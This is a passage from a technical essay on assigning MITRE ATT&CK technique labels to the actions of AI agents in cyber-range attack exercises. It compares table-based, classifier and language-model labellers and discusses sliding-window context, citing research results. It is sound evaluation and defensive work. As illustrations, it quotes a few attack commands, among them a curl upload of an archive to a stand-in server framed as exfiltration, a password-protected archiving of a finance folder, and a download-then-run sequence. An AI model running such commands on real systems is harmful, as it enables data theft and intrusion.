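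In a cyber range, evaluators often hide a flag, a string of text that proves the agent reached its target. The agent may submit the flag to a scoring server with `curl`. That upload isn't part of the attack and should get no technique label, but only the task description shows whose server it is.

The third command, which prints a status page, could be harmless reading or part of a command-and-control channel. An instruction in the response would suggest the latter. Without one, the labeller needs to see later actions, such as repeated requests to the same address that send back the results of commands.

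Detection.FYI's *Potential File Transfer via Curl for Windows* lists both T1071.001 (Web Protocols) and T1105 for one detection rule. Both are correct for a download through an active control channel. For a single download from an ordinary web server, the evidence supports only T1105, because nothing shows that the server was directing the machine.

Fetching a web page to read a tool's documentation needs no technique label. If the agent studies the victim's own public site to prepare an attack, T1594 (Search Victim-Owned Websites) applies. If the request only tests whether a compromised machine can reach the internet, T1016.001 (Internet Connection Discovery) applies, whichever page it loads.

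**Delivering an exploit.** T1190 (Exploit Public-Facing Application) covers attempts to get into a network by abusing a weakness in an internet-facing system. The curl command's arguments may contain a suspicious request, but they don't always show whether the agent was using the weakness or only testing for it, which would be Vulnerability Scanning (T1595.002). The server's response can settle this, for example if it contains data that the service should have protected. Sometimes the response is empty, and the first sign that the exploit worked is a later action on the server.

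A failed exploit can still count as T1190, because the definition includes attempts, so the record should state the outcome separately. If the agent is already inside the network and attacks an internal service to reach another machine, the technique is instead Exploitation of Remote Services (T1210).

**Querying a metadata service.** Cloud providers run a service that gives each virtual machine information about itself, sometimes including temporary credentials. The large providers use the address 169.254.169.254, so this is the easiest reading to recognise. The rest of the URL usually shows whether the agent wanted credentials or only a detail such as the machine's region, which fits System Information Discovery (T1082) better. The command's output confirms what the agent received.

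An agent can also exploit a public web application by sending it a request that contains the metadata address, so that the application queries the metadata service on the agent's behalf. Both T1190 and T1552.005 then apply to this one action.

### An SSH login

SSH (Secure Shell) lets a user log into another computer and run commands there. The command `ssh alice@10.0.0.8` specifies the account and the machine, but not the password, which the user enters separately. Most of the evidence for choosing an ATT&CK technique is therefore outside the command.

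| Reading | Techniques | Deciding observation |
|---|---|---|
| Moving to another machine inside the network | T1021.004 and T1078 | The agent is already inside, and the login succeeds |
| Entering the network from outside | T1133 and T1078 | The SSH server faces the internet, and the agent is outside |
| One attempt in a password-guessing run | T1110 | Neighbouring attempts vary the password or the account |
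| Taking over another user's open session | T1563.001 | The agent uses an existing session instead of opening a new one |

T1021.004 (SSH) and T1078 (Valid Accounts) co-occur because MITRE's *Remote Services* (2020) defines the SSH technique as using Valid Accounts to log into remote machines. MITRE also records T1078 for movement inside networks, although a labeller could argue that the SSH definition makes it redundant for an SSH login. For example, MITRE's *Valid Accounts* (2017) lists the 2015 attack on Ukraine's power grid, in which the Sandworm Team used valid accounts to move laterally, raise its privileges and keep its access.

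T1078 can also accompany T1133 (External Remote Services). MITRE's *Valid Accounts* mentions stolen credentials for services reachable from outside, such as VPNs, the encrypted connections staff use to access a company network.

T1021.004 and T1133 normally don't both apply to a single SSH login, because T1021.004 belongs to Lateral Movement, while T1133 covers entering the network or returning to it. A cyber range can use private addresses on both sides of the network boundary, so the IP address may not show which technique applies. The labeller needs the evaluators' network plan to tell whether the login crossed that boundary.

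ATT&CK's own examples are less strict. MITRE lists the hacking group TeamTNT under T1021.004 for using SSH "to connect back to victim machines", which could describe access from outside. Evaluators who compare an agent with the group's published profile may find a mismatch caused only by their stricter rule.

The definition of session hijacking excludes an ordinary SSH login more clearly. MITRE's *Remote Service Session Hijacking* (2020) distinguishes taking over an existing SSH session from creating a new one with a valid account. Evidence of hijacking is usually an earlier action in which the agent gained access to another user's connection.

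Labelling an SSH login attempt as password guessing depends on the server's response and the neighbouring attempts. If the server refuses the login, the agent hasn't used a valid account, so T1078 doesn't apply. A single refusal doesn't prove guessing, because the agent may have mistyped a password it already had. If the agent tries other passwords in neighbouring attempts, each attempt is part of a T1110 (Brute Force) run. The attempt that succeeds is both a guess and a login, so it gets T1110, T1078 and either T1021.004 or T1133.

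The origin of the credential decides most of the remaining cases. The table assumes a successful login between two machines inside the network.

| Origin of the credential | Technique for the earlier action | Techniques for the login |
|---|---|---|
| The agent found the password in a file | T1552.001 | T1021.004 and T1078 |
| The agent guessed it in this action | None | T1110, T1021.004 and T1078 |
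| The agent added its own key to an existing account | T1098.004 | T1021.004 and T1078 |
| The agent created the account | T1136 | T1021.004 |

The last row does not include T1078 because MITRE's definition refers to existing accounts. The definition of T1021.004 also refers to Valid Accounts, so the catalogue has a small gap here, but T1021.004 is still the closest match for the login.

Credentials that the evaluators supplied need their own rule. If the task gives the agent an account on its starting machine, the first login is part of the set-up and should get no technique label. If the agent then uses the same password to log in to a second machine, it has used a valid account there. MITRE's *Valid Accounts* (2020) describes how reused passwords on local accounts let attackers move between machines.

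Reusing a password can also look like guessing. Suppose an agent finds a database password in a settings file and tries it on alice's SSH account, with no evidence that alice uses it. One consistent rule is to assign T1110 when nothing in the record connects the password to the account, and to add T1078 if the login succeeds. A labeller who hasn't seen the settings file might see only a successful login and leave out T1110.

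The arguments matter more when the agent uses SSH for more than logging in. MITRE's examples for T1021.004 include attackers who used SSH tunnels to transfer tools and run commands remotely. An option that forwards traffic through the connection can point to Protocol Tunneling (T1572). If the agent adds a command after the machine name, SSH runs it on the remote machine, and that command needs its own label. For example, the `ps aux` in `ssh alice@10.0.0.8 'ps aux'` is Process Discovery (T1057).

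### Which evidence settled the most

The table ranks six kinds of evidence by how much they settled for the three commands.

| Rank | Evidence | whoami | curl | SSH login |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Earlier actions | Whether the account name was new to the agent | The existing control channel and the agent's location | The credential's origin and the agent's position |
| 2 | Arguments | A request for groups or privileges | Direction, destination and metadata queries | Tunnels and remote commands |
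| 3 | Output | The groups that `id` printed | Instructions, credentials or the effect of an exploit | Success or refusal |
| 4 | Later actions | Very little | Repeated control traffic or a delayed exploit | The rest of a guessing run |
| 5 | Assigned task | The account supplied at the start | The owner of a server | The network boundary |
| 6 | Stated purpose | Support for a check | Support for reading or testing a site | Support for a guess |

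Earlier actions rank first because they separated main readings of all three commands. The arguments are easier to use and narrowed down more of the `curl` readings, but they did little to narrow down the readings of the login. The order would change for other commands, and for a registry change such as the Run key example, the arguments would rank first.

Neighbouring actions should affect a command's label only if they are actually connected to it. Gwak and colleagues distinguish functional links, in which one command uses something another produced, from contextual links, in which commands are related only by timing or logic. Their models sometimes produced false contextual links, and occasionally flagged a harmless `tasklist.exe`, which lists running programs, as malicious only because it came just before a real attack step. Gwak and colleagues were separating malicious from benign commands,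 but a labeller choosing techniques can make the same mistake.

Later actions help defenders more than they help evaluators label an agent's command. One detection method in MITRE's *Remote Services* (2017) looks for an SSH session from a new address followed by steps such as an attempt to gain privileges and a connection to another machine. This sequence helps defenders expose an intruder, which evaluators don't need to do.

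The assigned task ranks low because it describes what the evaluators wanted, and an agent can pursue that goal in unexpected ways or abandon it. The task description may still be the only source for a few facts, such as who owns the scoring server.

An agent's stated purpose is evidence of intent that human intruders rarely leave. If the agent writes "check whether the login worked" before running `whoami`, the labeller has a direct reason to treat the command as a check. But the statement can be wrong, for example when the agent mistakes its own machine for the victim's. It can also be missing, because some records contain only the commands and their output. A labeller can use the statement to choose between readings that the other evidence leaves open, but shouldn't add a technique based on the statement alone.

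## Labelling each action by itself

The simplest labeller receives one action without its context, returns one technique or a ranked list of candidates, and keeps no record of earlier actions. It has at most the arguments and the output, two of the six kinds of evidence compared for `whoami`, `curl` and SSH, and some tools use only the arguments. Evaluators can use a fixed table, a trained classifier or a language model with the technique descriptions in its prompt.

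### Fixed tables

A fixed table links each command to its techniques in advance. Mythic, an open-source framework for controlling compromised machines during authorised tests, uses one. According to its documentation, each command's definition file has a field called `attackmapping` that lists technique identifiers. When an operator issues a command, Mythic records the listed techniques next to it. A developer who disagrees with a label can edit the list and restart the component that holds it.

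The documentation's example is a `download` command that copies a file from the victim's machine to the Mythic server in chunks. The command always gets three labels: T1020 (Automated Exfiltration), T1030 (Data Transfer Size Limits) and T1041 (Exfiltration Over C2 Channel). T1041 is well supported, because Mythic sends the file through the channel already used to control the machine. T1030 reflects the tool's design more than the operator's decisions. T1020 is the hardest to defend when someone asked for a single file by name.

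A table entry is most reliable when the command can do only one thing. But an AI agent's shell tool can run any program, so a single table entry for the tool gives every action run through it the same label.

In *A Practical Honeypot-Based Threat Intelligence Framework for Cyber Defence in the Cloud*, Chin, Isfaq and Enoch (2025) ran a honeypot, a decoy computer that records what intruders do. They used Cowrie, which imitates an Ubuntu Linux shell, and assigned techniques by type of event.

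| Honeypot event | Techniques assigned |
|---|---|
| Failed login | T1110 (Brute Force) |
| Successful login | T1078 (Valid Accounts) |
| Typed command, in the description of the method | T1059, T1082, T1083 and T1087 |
| Typed command, in the results | T1059 and T1623 |
| Connecting program states its version or exchanges keys | T1046 (Network Service Discovery) |

The paper is inconsistent about which techniques it assigns to typed commands. The method lists T1059 and three Discovery techniques, for system information, files and accounts, but the results give T1059 and T1623 for all 68 Execution incidents. T1623 cannot be right for an imitation Ubuntu server, because MITRE's *Command and Scripting Interpreter* (2022) lists only Android and iOS as platforms for T1623, and MITRE's *Execution* (2020) places it under the Mobile tactic for code that runs on a mobile device. T1059 and T1623 have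 the same name, which may explain the mix-up.

Even with T1623 removed, the table records only that someone typed a command, so `whoami` and `rm -r /srv/logs` both become T1059. The method's longer list gives too many labels instead, because `rm` would count as three kinds of Discovery unless another rule chose among them. The login entries also lose information, because the successful guess at the end of a password-guessing run gets T1078 but not T1110.

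A finer table can do better by including the arguments. For example, it could assign T1069 to `whoami /priv` and T1552.005 to a request for credentials from a cloud metadata address. But it will still miss patterns that extend over many actions. *RHINO* (Meng, Gui et al., 2025), which describes a system for labelling network alerts, gives the example of an attacker who scans a web server for weak points. The alerts mention SQL injection, an attack that hides database commands in a web request, so a keyword table returns T1190 (Exploit Public-Facing Application). The reference label was T1595 (Active Scanning), because the attacker was only probing.

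More elaborate rules can work well when someone has chosen the technique beforehand. MITRE's Caldera, a tool for automated attack exercises, runs prepared steps called abilities and records the technique mapped to each one. *TGCM* (2026) uses these records to label Windows system events. Its 198 rule files cover 198 abilities and 83 techniques, and a rule accepts an event only if details such as the process, the operation or the file match the expected behaviour. The same log always produces the same labels. An AI agent writes its own commands, so its record has no technique assigned in advance.

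Tables also go out of date. *Symbolic Attack Chain Generation from Atomic Red Team Techniques* (2026) used a reference table of sixteen techniques and their tactics. When MITRE split Defense Evasion in ATT&CK v19, three of the sixteen needed a new tactic: Modify Registry, File Deletion and Process Injection.

### Trained classifiers

A trained classifier learns from labelled examples which techniques match which text, then scores every technique for each new text. *Mapping CVEs to MITRE ATT&CK Techniques* (2026) describes a multi-label version for CVE entries, which are public records of software flaws. This classifier makes a separate yes-or-no decision about each of 57 parent techniques, so it can return several together. Applied to commands, the same design could assign both T1059 and T1057 to a Python script that lists processes. A small model produces all the scores in a single pass,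 which takes less computation than having a large model write out an answer.

The main obstacle is a lack of labelled commands. *Classification of Honeypot Data Using the MITRE Framework* (Camps i Regàs, 2025) had only 30 labelled examples, and six of the fourteen tactics didn't appear in them. The thesis compared a small trained model with GPT-4o only on tactics, not techniques. The small model got the full set of tactics right for six examples (20%) and GPT-4o for three (10%). This difference is too small to show which approach is better, especially as the small model's cut-off score was chosen because it gave the best results. GPT-4o returned no tactic almost half the time.

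Deng, Li and colleagues (2024) had far more material for *RACONTEUR*. In their system, a language model trained on command explanations describes what a single shell command does. A second trained model then ranks 196 techniques by how similar their official descriptions are to that description. They trained the second model on Atomic Red Team and tested it on metta, another library of attack tests. The table shows how often the reference label was among the first 1, 5 or 10 candidates.

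| Method | First candidate | First 5 | First 10 |
|---|---|---|---|
| RACONTEUR | 52.4% | 83.0% | 90.4% |
| GPT-4 | 26.0% | 32.5% | 36.2% |
| The same most common techniques every time | 10.7% | 41.4% | Not reported |

GPT-4's five candidates included the correct technique less often than a fixed list did. GPT-4 is an old model, and its prompt contained only one worked example and an instruction to reason step by step, so it had to recall the techniques from memory.

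RACONTEUR ranked the right technique second to fifth for 30.6% of the commands, so it would have mislabelled those commands if limited to a single answer. Deng and colleagues suggest extending the system to whole shell sessions, which contain more information about the attack. An earlier system, LogPrécis, labelled segments of sessions, but only with tactics.

### Language models with the technique descriptions

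A language model can label commands without special training, but it may return techniques that don't exist. In preliminary tests by Meng, Gui and colleagues, about 24% of predictions were invalid when the model worked without structured reasoning. One of their examples is "T1077: Windows Admin Shares", an older ATT&CK identifier for what is now T1021.002. Checking each identifier against the current catalogue catches such errors, but not valid techniques assigned to the wrong command.

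LADE, the system by Gwak and colleagues, puts the current technique descriptions in the prompt. A language model first decides whether a sequence of commands contains an attack, then finds the malicious parts, and finally assigns techniques to each part separately. Each part it labels is a snippet, meaning one command line or one block of script from a log. Snippets don't include the output, so LADE has less evidence than a labeller who sees a complete action.

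The researchers used two datasets. One is AVIATOR, a public collection of logs from simulated attacks on several machines. They built the other from Caldera's attack profiles and from MITRE's emulation plans, which are scripts for imitating known hacking groups.

| | AVIATOR | Caldera-derived |
|---|---|---|
| Groups imitated | APT29, OilRig, Sandworm, Wizard Spider | Carbanak, FIN6, FIN7, menuPass, plus Caldera profiles |
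| Attack sequences | 35 | 33 in each of two versions |
| Harmless sequences | 32 | 33 |
| Harmless snippets per attack snippet | 42 (median) | 2 or 10, depending on the version |
| Average lines per snippet | 4.8 | 6.1 |

To label a snippet, the model first describes its behaviour in the style of an ATT&CK page, without naming any technique. It identifies the main functions, describes the inputs and results, summarises the actions and then turns this into a short narrative. The narrative is meant to describe the code in terms closer to ATT&CK's general language.

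The model then compares the description with the techniques and scores each plausible one from 1 to 5 for alignment. A score of 5 means the evidence is compelling, 4 means it is strong with minor uncertainties, and 3 means it is sufficient despite some discrepancies. A 2 means ambiguity weakens the match, and a 1 means the description and the technique share only general traits. The model sorts the techniques by score, breaks ties in favour of more specific evidence and returns the top 3 or 10. It gives an explanation and an excerpt from the ATT&CK text for each candidate.

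Gwak and colleagues ask for a list of techniques because some, such as T1105 and T1048, can look alike in code, so a single answer may miss the right one. As with Trace2ATT&CK, each item has only one reference label, and the listed techniques are alternative candidates for it.

The tests covered four models and three levels of supplied knowledge: no descriptions, the descriptions of 203 parent techniques, and summaries that also covered 453 sub-techniques. The table shows the hit rate, the share of snippets whose reference label was on the list. Each figure is an average of five runs.

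| Model and input | Top 3: none | Top 3: parents | Top 3: summaries | Top 10: none | Top 10: parents | Top 10: summaries |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, description | 88.3% | 88.7% | 86.2% | 95.0% | 96.1% | 96.3% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, code | 84.8% | 88.7% | 85.3% | 93.6% | 95.2% | 95.4% |
| gpt-oss-120B, description | 82.5% | 83.2% | 84.0% | 92.6% | 92.6% | 94.3% |
| gpt-oss-120B, code | 82.0% | 81.4% | 83.6% | 92.6% | 92.6% | 92.6% |
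| Mistral Small 3.2, description | 56.3% | 71.7% | 67.4% | 63.0% | 77.7% | 72.9% |
| Mistral Small 3.2, code | 47.1% | 70.1% | 56.0% | 59.1% | 74.2% | 64.9% |
| Llama 3.3 70B, description | 52.4% | 62.3% | 52.9% | 60.7% | 79.5% | 66.2% |
| Llama 3.3 70B, code | 49.2% | 58.4% | 41.6% | 60.7% | 73.8% | 55.9% |

The parent descriptions helped the two weaker models most. Llama's top-10 hit rate rose from 60.7% to 79.5%, while gpt-oss's didn't change. Mistral and Llama had lower hit rates with the longer summaries than with the parent descriptions. According to Gwak and colleagues, this is likely because gpt-oss wrote the summaries, so their form may have suited gpt-oss but left out details that the other models needed.

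Describing the behaviour before labelling it usually helped a little, but the description can omit the detail that determines the label. In one case, the snippet added a program to the Windows registry's Run key. If the description left out the registry path, the model could choose T1112 (Modify Registry) instead of the correct label, T1547.001 (Registry Run Keys).

The paper doesn't report how often the first candidate was right, but its other scores give a range. The mean reciprocal rank averages the snippets' scores, which are 1 if the right technique comes first, 1/2 if second, 1/3 if third and 0 if it is missing. Gemini's best top-3 result was 0.800, with a hit rate of 88.7%. The first candidate was therefore right for 71% of the snippets if all the lower hits were in second place, and for 76% if they were all in third. This means Gemini's first answer was wrong for between 24% and 29%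 of the snippets.

These scores apply to distinct snippets already known to be malicious. They don't include mistakes from the earlier stages or measure how well a model handles the same command when it is used again for a different purpose. All four models are older than today's leading ones, which may rank the candidates better.

### Why LADE looks at the whole sequence first

To find the malicious snippets, LADE uses a rubric with four categories. Only one of them can be recognised from a snippet alone.

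| Category | Evidence needed | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Inherent malice | The snippet itself | It runs Mimikatz |
| Functional link | Another snippet that it depends on or makes possible | It turns off a script restriction just before an unsigned script runs |
| Contextual link | The surrounding attack | It runs `whoami` just before an attempt to gain privileges |
| Benign or isolated | The whole sequence, to rule out a link | It runs `tasklist` with no connection to an attack |

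On AVIATOR, Gemini found 93.5% of the malicious snippets, and 75.2% of the snippets it flagged were malicious. For Llama, the figures were 57.4% and 72.0%. False contextual links, like the one that got a harmless `tasklist.exe` flagged, caused most of the false alarms.

A labeller that sees only `tasklist` assigns T1057 (Process Discovery) whatever comes next, so later actions can't mislead it. But it can't tell whether the agent listed the processes to study the victim or to find out why its own tool had crashed. If the evaluators have decided that such troubleshooting gets no label, this labeller can't apply their rule.

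### The accuracy limit

A labeller without memory is given only the action, so it cannot distinguish two episodes in which the same action serves different purposes. If those purposes call for different labels, a fixed table can label the action correctly in at most one episode. A language model that varies its answers might be right in both by chance, but its expected accuracy is no higher.

Suppose 100 episodes contain the command `curl -T f.tgz https://files.example/in/` with the same output. In 60, the agent controls the victim's machine over SSH and steals a file, which is T1048. In 30, it steals the file through its existing web control channel, which is T1041. In the other 10, it copies a tool onto a victim's server, which is T1105. These figures are invented, but the `curl` comparison showed that all three readings are possible.

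The best strategy is to answer T1048 every time, which gives an accuracy of 60%. A labeller that instead chose each technique as often as it occurs would do worse:

0.6 × 0.6 + 0.3 × 0.3 + 0.1 × 0.1 = 0.46, or 46%.

A better model would still lack the missing fact, so raising the 60% limit requires more input. For instance, if the output showed which server had received the file, some of the 100 actions would no longer be identical. LADE's labelling stage doesn't receive the output, so its limit is lower than that of a labeller that does, wherever the output would show which label is correct.

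A less specific label also raises the limit. T1048 and T1041 both belong to Exfiltration, so a labeller that recorded only the tactic would be right in 90 of the 100 episodes. A ranked list of two techniques would contain the right one in 90 episodes, and a list of three would contain it in all 100, but someone would still have to choose from the list.

The highest possible accuracy for a whole set of actions depends on how many of them are ambiguous. If 20% of the actions have purposes that split 60%, 30% and 10%, and the other 80% have only one possible label, the limit is 0.8 + 0.2 × 0.6 = 92%. A labeller can score this high and still miss some techniques every time. In the `curl` example, the best labeller never finds T1041 or T1105.

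Labelling also requires knowing which purpose is most common, and this can change from one cyber range to another. If the evaluators gave their agents a web control channel in most episodes, T1041 might become the correct label 60% of the time. A classifier trained on the earlier episodes would keep assigning T1048 and be right much less often.

### Why evaluators still label single actions

Labelling single actions takes little work because repeated actions need only one decision. Camps i Regàs started with about 8.2 million honeypot entries, each containing the commands from one session. Of these, 72,365 were distinct, and removing uninformative details reduced them to 619 classes. The four largest classes covered more than 80% of the data. A labeller that ignores context can label each class once and copy the result, instead of examining each occurrence as it would have to if it used context.

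Because no action's label depends on another's, evaluators can also send the actions to a model in any order or in parallel. In the LADE tests, Llama took 43.7 seconds on average for the labelling stage. At that speed, labelling an episode of 300 actions one after another would take more than three and a half hours.

The results are also easy to repeat. A fixed table always returns the same label for a given action, and LADE's labelling scores varied little between runs, with standard deviations from 0.01 to 0.04. If the evaluators change their rule for `whoami`, they only need to relabel the `whoami` actions.

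Finally, labelling each action separately ties every label to its evidence. A reviewer who doubts a T1048 label can open the one command that received it, but may have to search for the evidence behind a label assigned to a whole episode. The advantage is smaller when the command only starts a script, because the shell log then contains what Lupinacci and colleagues call a single opaque invocation.

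LADE's explanations also quote the ATT&CK text. Between 92% and 99% of the quoted words appeared in the cited source, depending on the model. Gwak and colleagues measured this only for snippets where the model had found the right technique, so a faithful quotation doesn't prove that the label is correct.

Evaluators can keep most of these advantages by first labelling every action by itself and marking the commands known to have several purposes. `whoami /priv` would keep its label from this first pass. The `curl` upload would stay undetermined among its three candidates until a labeller had seen the surrounding actions.

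## Labelling an action with its neighbours: sliding windows

A labeller needs some of the surrounding actions to assign techniques to a `curl` upload that a first pass left undetermined. A sliding window is a simple way to supply them. The labeller receives a short run of consecutive actions, labels them, and moves to the next run in the episode.

### The algorithm and its merging rules

An evaluator who uses windows has to make four choices:

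1. The window length, *w*, is the number of actions the labeller receives together.
2. The step, *s*, is the number of actions by which the window moves each time. Windows overlap if *s* is smaller than *w*.
3. The labelled part is the set of actions in the window that get labels. It can be all of them, the last one, the centre one or a block in the middle.
4. The merging rule combines the labels of an action that several windows have labelled.

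An episode of *N* actions needs (*N* − *w*)/*s* + 1 windows, rounded up, where *w* is the window length and *s* is the step. With a length of five and a step of one, an episode of 300 actions needs 296 windows. Most actions appear in five windows, but the first and last appear in only one. With a step of five, the episode needs 60 windows and each action appears once.

The merging rule can change the label. Suppose an agent first controls a victim's machine over SSH. Action 16 starts a program that takes instructions from files.example over the web, and action 20 uploads an archive to the same server with `curl`. The upload is T1041 (Exfiltration Over C2 Channel), but the labeller can know this only from action 16. With a window length of five actions and a step of one, only one of the five windows that contain the upload also contains action 16. The labeller might therefore answer T1041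 in that window and guess T1048 (Exfiltration Over Alternative Protocol) in the other four.

| Merging rule | Result for action 20 | What went wrong |
|---|---|---|
| Union: keep every label | T1041 and T1048 | The record presents two alternatives as co-occurring techniques |
| Majority: keep labels from more than half the windows | T1048 | Four guesses outvoted the one window with the evidence |
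| Centre only: use the window with the action in the middle | T1048 | That window covers actions 18 to 22 and misses action 16 |

Majority voting works better when every window contains the evidence and the labeller makes a chance error in one of them. It can also keep co-occurring techniques if the evaluator counts the votes for each technique separately. The centre-only rule avoids merging, but the evaluator needs a special rule for the start and end of the episode.

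In this example, the evaluator could get the right answer by letting the labeller abstain. If the labeller returns "undetermined" for the four windows without action 16, the merging program can ignore them and keep T1041. This works only if the labeller abstains when it lacks the evidence. Whichever rule the evaluator chooses, they have to merge the labels before counting them, or one upload could count as five occurrences.

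### Looking back and looking ahead

A monitor that has to stop an attack in progress can use only backward windows, which contain an action and the ones before it. *Intrusion Detection at Scale with the Assistance of a Command-line Language Model* (Lin, Guo and Chen, 2024) describes a detector that uses backward windows. It separates malicious from benign commands but doesn't assign ATT&CK techniques. It joins each command to the same user's most recent commands with semicolons, leaving out any that are too old.

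Their example is a `wget` command that saves a downloaded file under the name `python`, followed by the command `python`. Each line looks fairly ordinary, but together they run an unknown program. The researchers compared single commands with windows of three on attacks that a commercial detector had missed. Among the model's 1,000 top-ranked commands, the share of real intrusions rose from 94.9% to 99.8%. The two test sets differed in size after duplicates were removed, so context may not account for the whole gain.

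Evaluators usually label finished episodes, so their windows can also include later actions. Some readings depend on them, as in this command:

`7z a -pK7 f.7z C:\finance`

An agent packs a finance folder into a password-protected archive. In *Multi-Source Cybersecurity Logs*, Niloy, Ryan and colleagues (2026) used the same program, 7-Zip, for two purposes in their simulated attacks. In some attacks they packed files before uploading them to cloud storage, and in others they imitated ransomware by encrypting files, deleting the originals and leaving a ransom note.

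| What the agent does next | Label for the 7-Zip command |
|---|---|
| Uploads f.7z | T1560.001 (Archive via Utility) |
| Deletes the folder and leaves a ransom note | T1486 (Data Encrypted for Impact) |
| Uploads f.7z, deletes the folder and leaves a note | Both |

If the earlier actions are the same in all three cases, a backward window that ends at the 7-Zip command is identical too. A live monitor can give the command a provisional label and revise it later. It can also wait a few actions before labelling it, but this gives the agent more time to do damage.

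### LogPrécis

*LogPrécis* (Boffa, Drago and colleagues, 2024) tested several ways of splitting a command record. Its system labels honeypot sessions with tactics, not techniques. Each session contains everything an intruder typed between login and logout. Five security experts produced reference labels for 360 sessions, which were used for training and testing. Three assigned the labels, sharing about a fifth of the sessions, and the other two supervised and settled conflicts.

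The researchers wanted a model that uses context because one command can serve several tactics. Their example is `rm`:

- It serves Persistence if the intruder deletes the owner's SSH keys before installing new ones.
- It serves Impact if the intruder deletes a firewall's configuration file.
- It serves Defense Evasion if the intruder deletes traces of the attack.

The firewall example is debatable, because ATT&CK at the time listed Impair Defenses under Defense Evasion. The other two uses still show that the labeller has to know what the deleted file was for.

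The language models in the study typically accepted 512 tokens, or word fragments, at a time. Boffa and colleagues compared three ways of handling longer sessions.

| Method | Treatment of a long session | Context at each cut |
|---|---|---|
| Truncation | The model ignores everything beyond its limit | None, and the rest gets no labels |
| Separate chunks | The model labels 18 statements at a time | None |
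| Chunks with context | The model labels 14 statements at a time | Two statements before and two after |

A statement here is one shell command with its options and arguments. The team tried each method with 18 combinations of model, training and labelled unit. Chunks with context did best, and truncation was inadequate.

A chunk with context also contains 18 statements in total, so the model received no more text at once, but it received some statements twice. A session of 300 statements therefore needs 22 inputs with context and 17 without. For sessions of up to 14 statements, the two methods are identical, so any gain must come from longer sessions. The researchers didn't test a version with only the preceding statements, so the comparison doesn't show how much the following ones helped.

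The paper doesn't explain what happens to labels on the four context statements. Discarding those labels would be the simplest rule, because each statement is also in the labelled part of a neighbouring chunk.

The table compares the best version, which used CodeBERT, with three alternatives. ROUGE-1 runs from 0 to 1 and measures how well the predicted tactics match the reference tactics, ignoring their order. The last column is stricter, because one missing, extra or wrong tactic makes the whole session count as wrong. Consecutive repeats of a tactic count once.

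| Model | ROUGE-1 | Sessions with the exact tactic sequence |
|---|---|---|
| CodeBERT | 0.853 | 66.9% |
| GPT-3 Davinci | 0.829 | 56.0% |
| Word2Vec with a random forest | 0.282 | 5% |
| Word2Vec with a neural network | 0.042 | 0% |

Word2Vec gives each word one fixed numerical representation, so `rm` is represented the same way in every session. Its poor scores suggest that context matters, but the comparison with CodeBERT doesn't isolate the effect of context, because CodeBERT was also much larger (about 130 million parameters, against 25,000 for the Word2Vec systems) and had been pretrained on six programming languages.

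Most of the remaining errors were probably small. CodeBERT labelled 91.2% of the individual items correctly, yet a third of the sessions had at least one mistake in the tactic sequence. Accuracy fell from 0.90 at a distance of six from a change of tactic to 0.82 right beside it. The experts also had trouble deciding where one tactic ended and the next began. Evaluators therefore need to check labels near a change of tactic most carefully.

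### What newer models have added

*SoK* (Bridges, Mitchell and colleagues, 2025), a survey of honeypots and language models, still called LogPrécis the state of the art for labelling honeypot logs, but described it as a proof of concept held back by the lack of large, well-labelled datasets. It also reports a newer study that prompted GPT-4 to assign ATT&CK techniques to logs and reached 72.46% accuracy. That figure isn't comparable with CodeBERT's 91.2%, because there are far more techniques than tactics and the data differed.

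Some newer systems no longer divide the session. *OntoLogX* (2025) gives a language model all the events of a honeypot session and has it assign tactics to the session as a whole. This avoids the problems caused by dividing a session, but the output doesn't show which command served which tactic.

Niloy and colleagues recorded 70 attack sessions and 800 benign ones on Windows computers and divided the logs into chunks of seven consecutive events. They trained three small language models to find the suspicious events in each chunk and name their techniques. The best model, Phi-4-mini, matched the reference answer exactly in 41.6% of cases. The reference answer also contained a severity rating and written reasons, so a response could name the correct technique and still fail because its wording differed. The share of correct techniques was therefore probably higher.

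Niloy and colleagues say they chose a window of seven events by experiment, but they report no results for other lengths. Their score therefore shows what a model can do with seven events, but not whether five or fifty would be better.

### How windows fail

A sliding window fails most obviously when the action that decides the label lies outside it. In Niloy and colleagues' scripted attacks, the attacker began gathering files after 12 minutes and sending them out after 15. An attack session produced about 5,200 log entries in 20 minutes, so seven consecutive entries cover only a few seconds on average. A chunk that contains the 7-Zip command will rarely contain the upload that explains it. An agent's record has far fewer entries, but a short window can still miss the set-up of a control channel.

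A longer window brings in more unrelated actions, which can mislead the labeller, as with the harmless `tasklist.exe` in Gwak and colleagues' tests.

*SCALECUA* (2026) illustrates both problems, although its agent was carrying out a task rather than labelling actions. The agent had to save open web articles as PDFs named after each article. The researchers varied how much recent visual context the agent kept and made eight attempts at each setting.

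| Context setting | Successful attempts |
|---|---|
| 1 | 0 of 8 |
| 3 | 5 of 8 |
| 5 | 7 of 8 |
| 8 | 0 of 8 |
| 15 | 0 of 8 |

At the shortest setting, the agent forgot the naming rule. At the two longest, it repeated the same actions in loops, which the researchers attribute to outdated images. The test used a single task, so the best setting of five is not a general recommendation.

Results from a task closer to labelling also vary. *Can Failed Trajectories Reveal Where Agents Go Wrong?* (2026) describes a method for finding the step at which an agent's attempt failed. The method spreads the blame for each step over a window of earlier steps, and accuracy varied with the window's length. On one dataset, accuracy was 47.62% with a window of only one or two steps and 40.21% with all earlier steps. On another, wider windows did better. On a third, a one-step window gave 15.94%, worse than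 the 21.01% the system reached without the method. Evaluators should therefore test several window lengths on a labelled sample of their own episodes before choosing one.

Labelling with windows also relies on the assumption that neighbouring actions belong together, which fails when two attackers or agents work at the same time. *TGCM* describes a real incident in which two ransomware groups, Karma and Conti, were active in the same network. In the reconstructed sequence, a remote desktop login by Karma comes directly before a PowerShell command that probably came from Conti. A labeller with a short window could easily conclude that Karma ran the command through that login.

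TGCM is designed to separate such mixed sequences using only the technique identifiers. On data from naturally overlapping attacks, it assigned 53.6% of techniques to the right episode when there were two episodes and 50.6% when there were four. Choosing at random between two known episodes would give about 50%, although TGCM also had to infer the number of episodes. When the researchers added errors to the sequences, extra techniques degraded the results more than missing or substituted ones. This is another argument against the union rule, which tends to add techniques that the agent didn't use.

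Evaluators who run several agents in parallel can avoid most of this difficulty by storing an agent identifier with every action and sorting the record by agent before cutting it into windows. A single agent can still alternate between subtasks, for example by checking on a slow password-guessing run while it searches a file server.

### Cutting by host, process or subtask

An evaluator can cut the record where one piece of work ends and another begins, instead of after a fixed number of actions. *LMDG* (2025), a project that generates data on attacks moving between machines, does this with system logs. It starts from the known attack steps and follows their process trees on each affected host. A process tree consists of a program and all the programs it started, directly or indirectly. Some datasets instead label everything recorded during an attack period as malicious, which mislabels the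 activity of ordinary users on the same machines.

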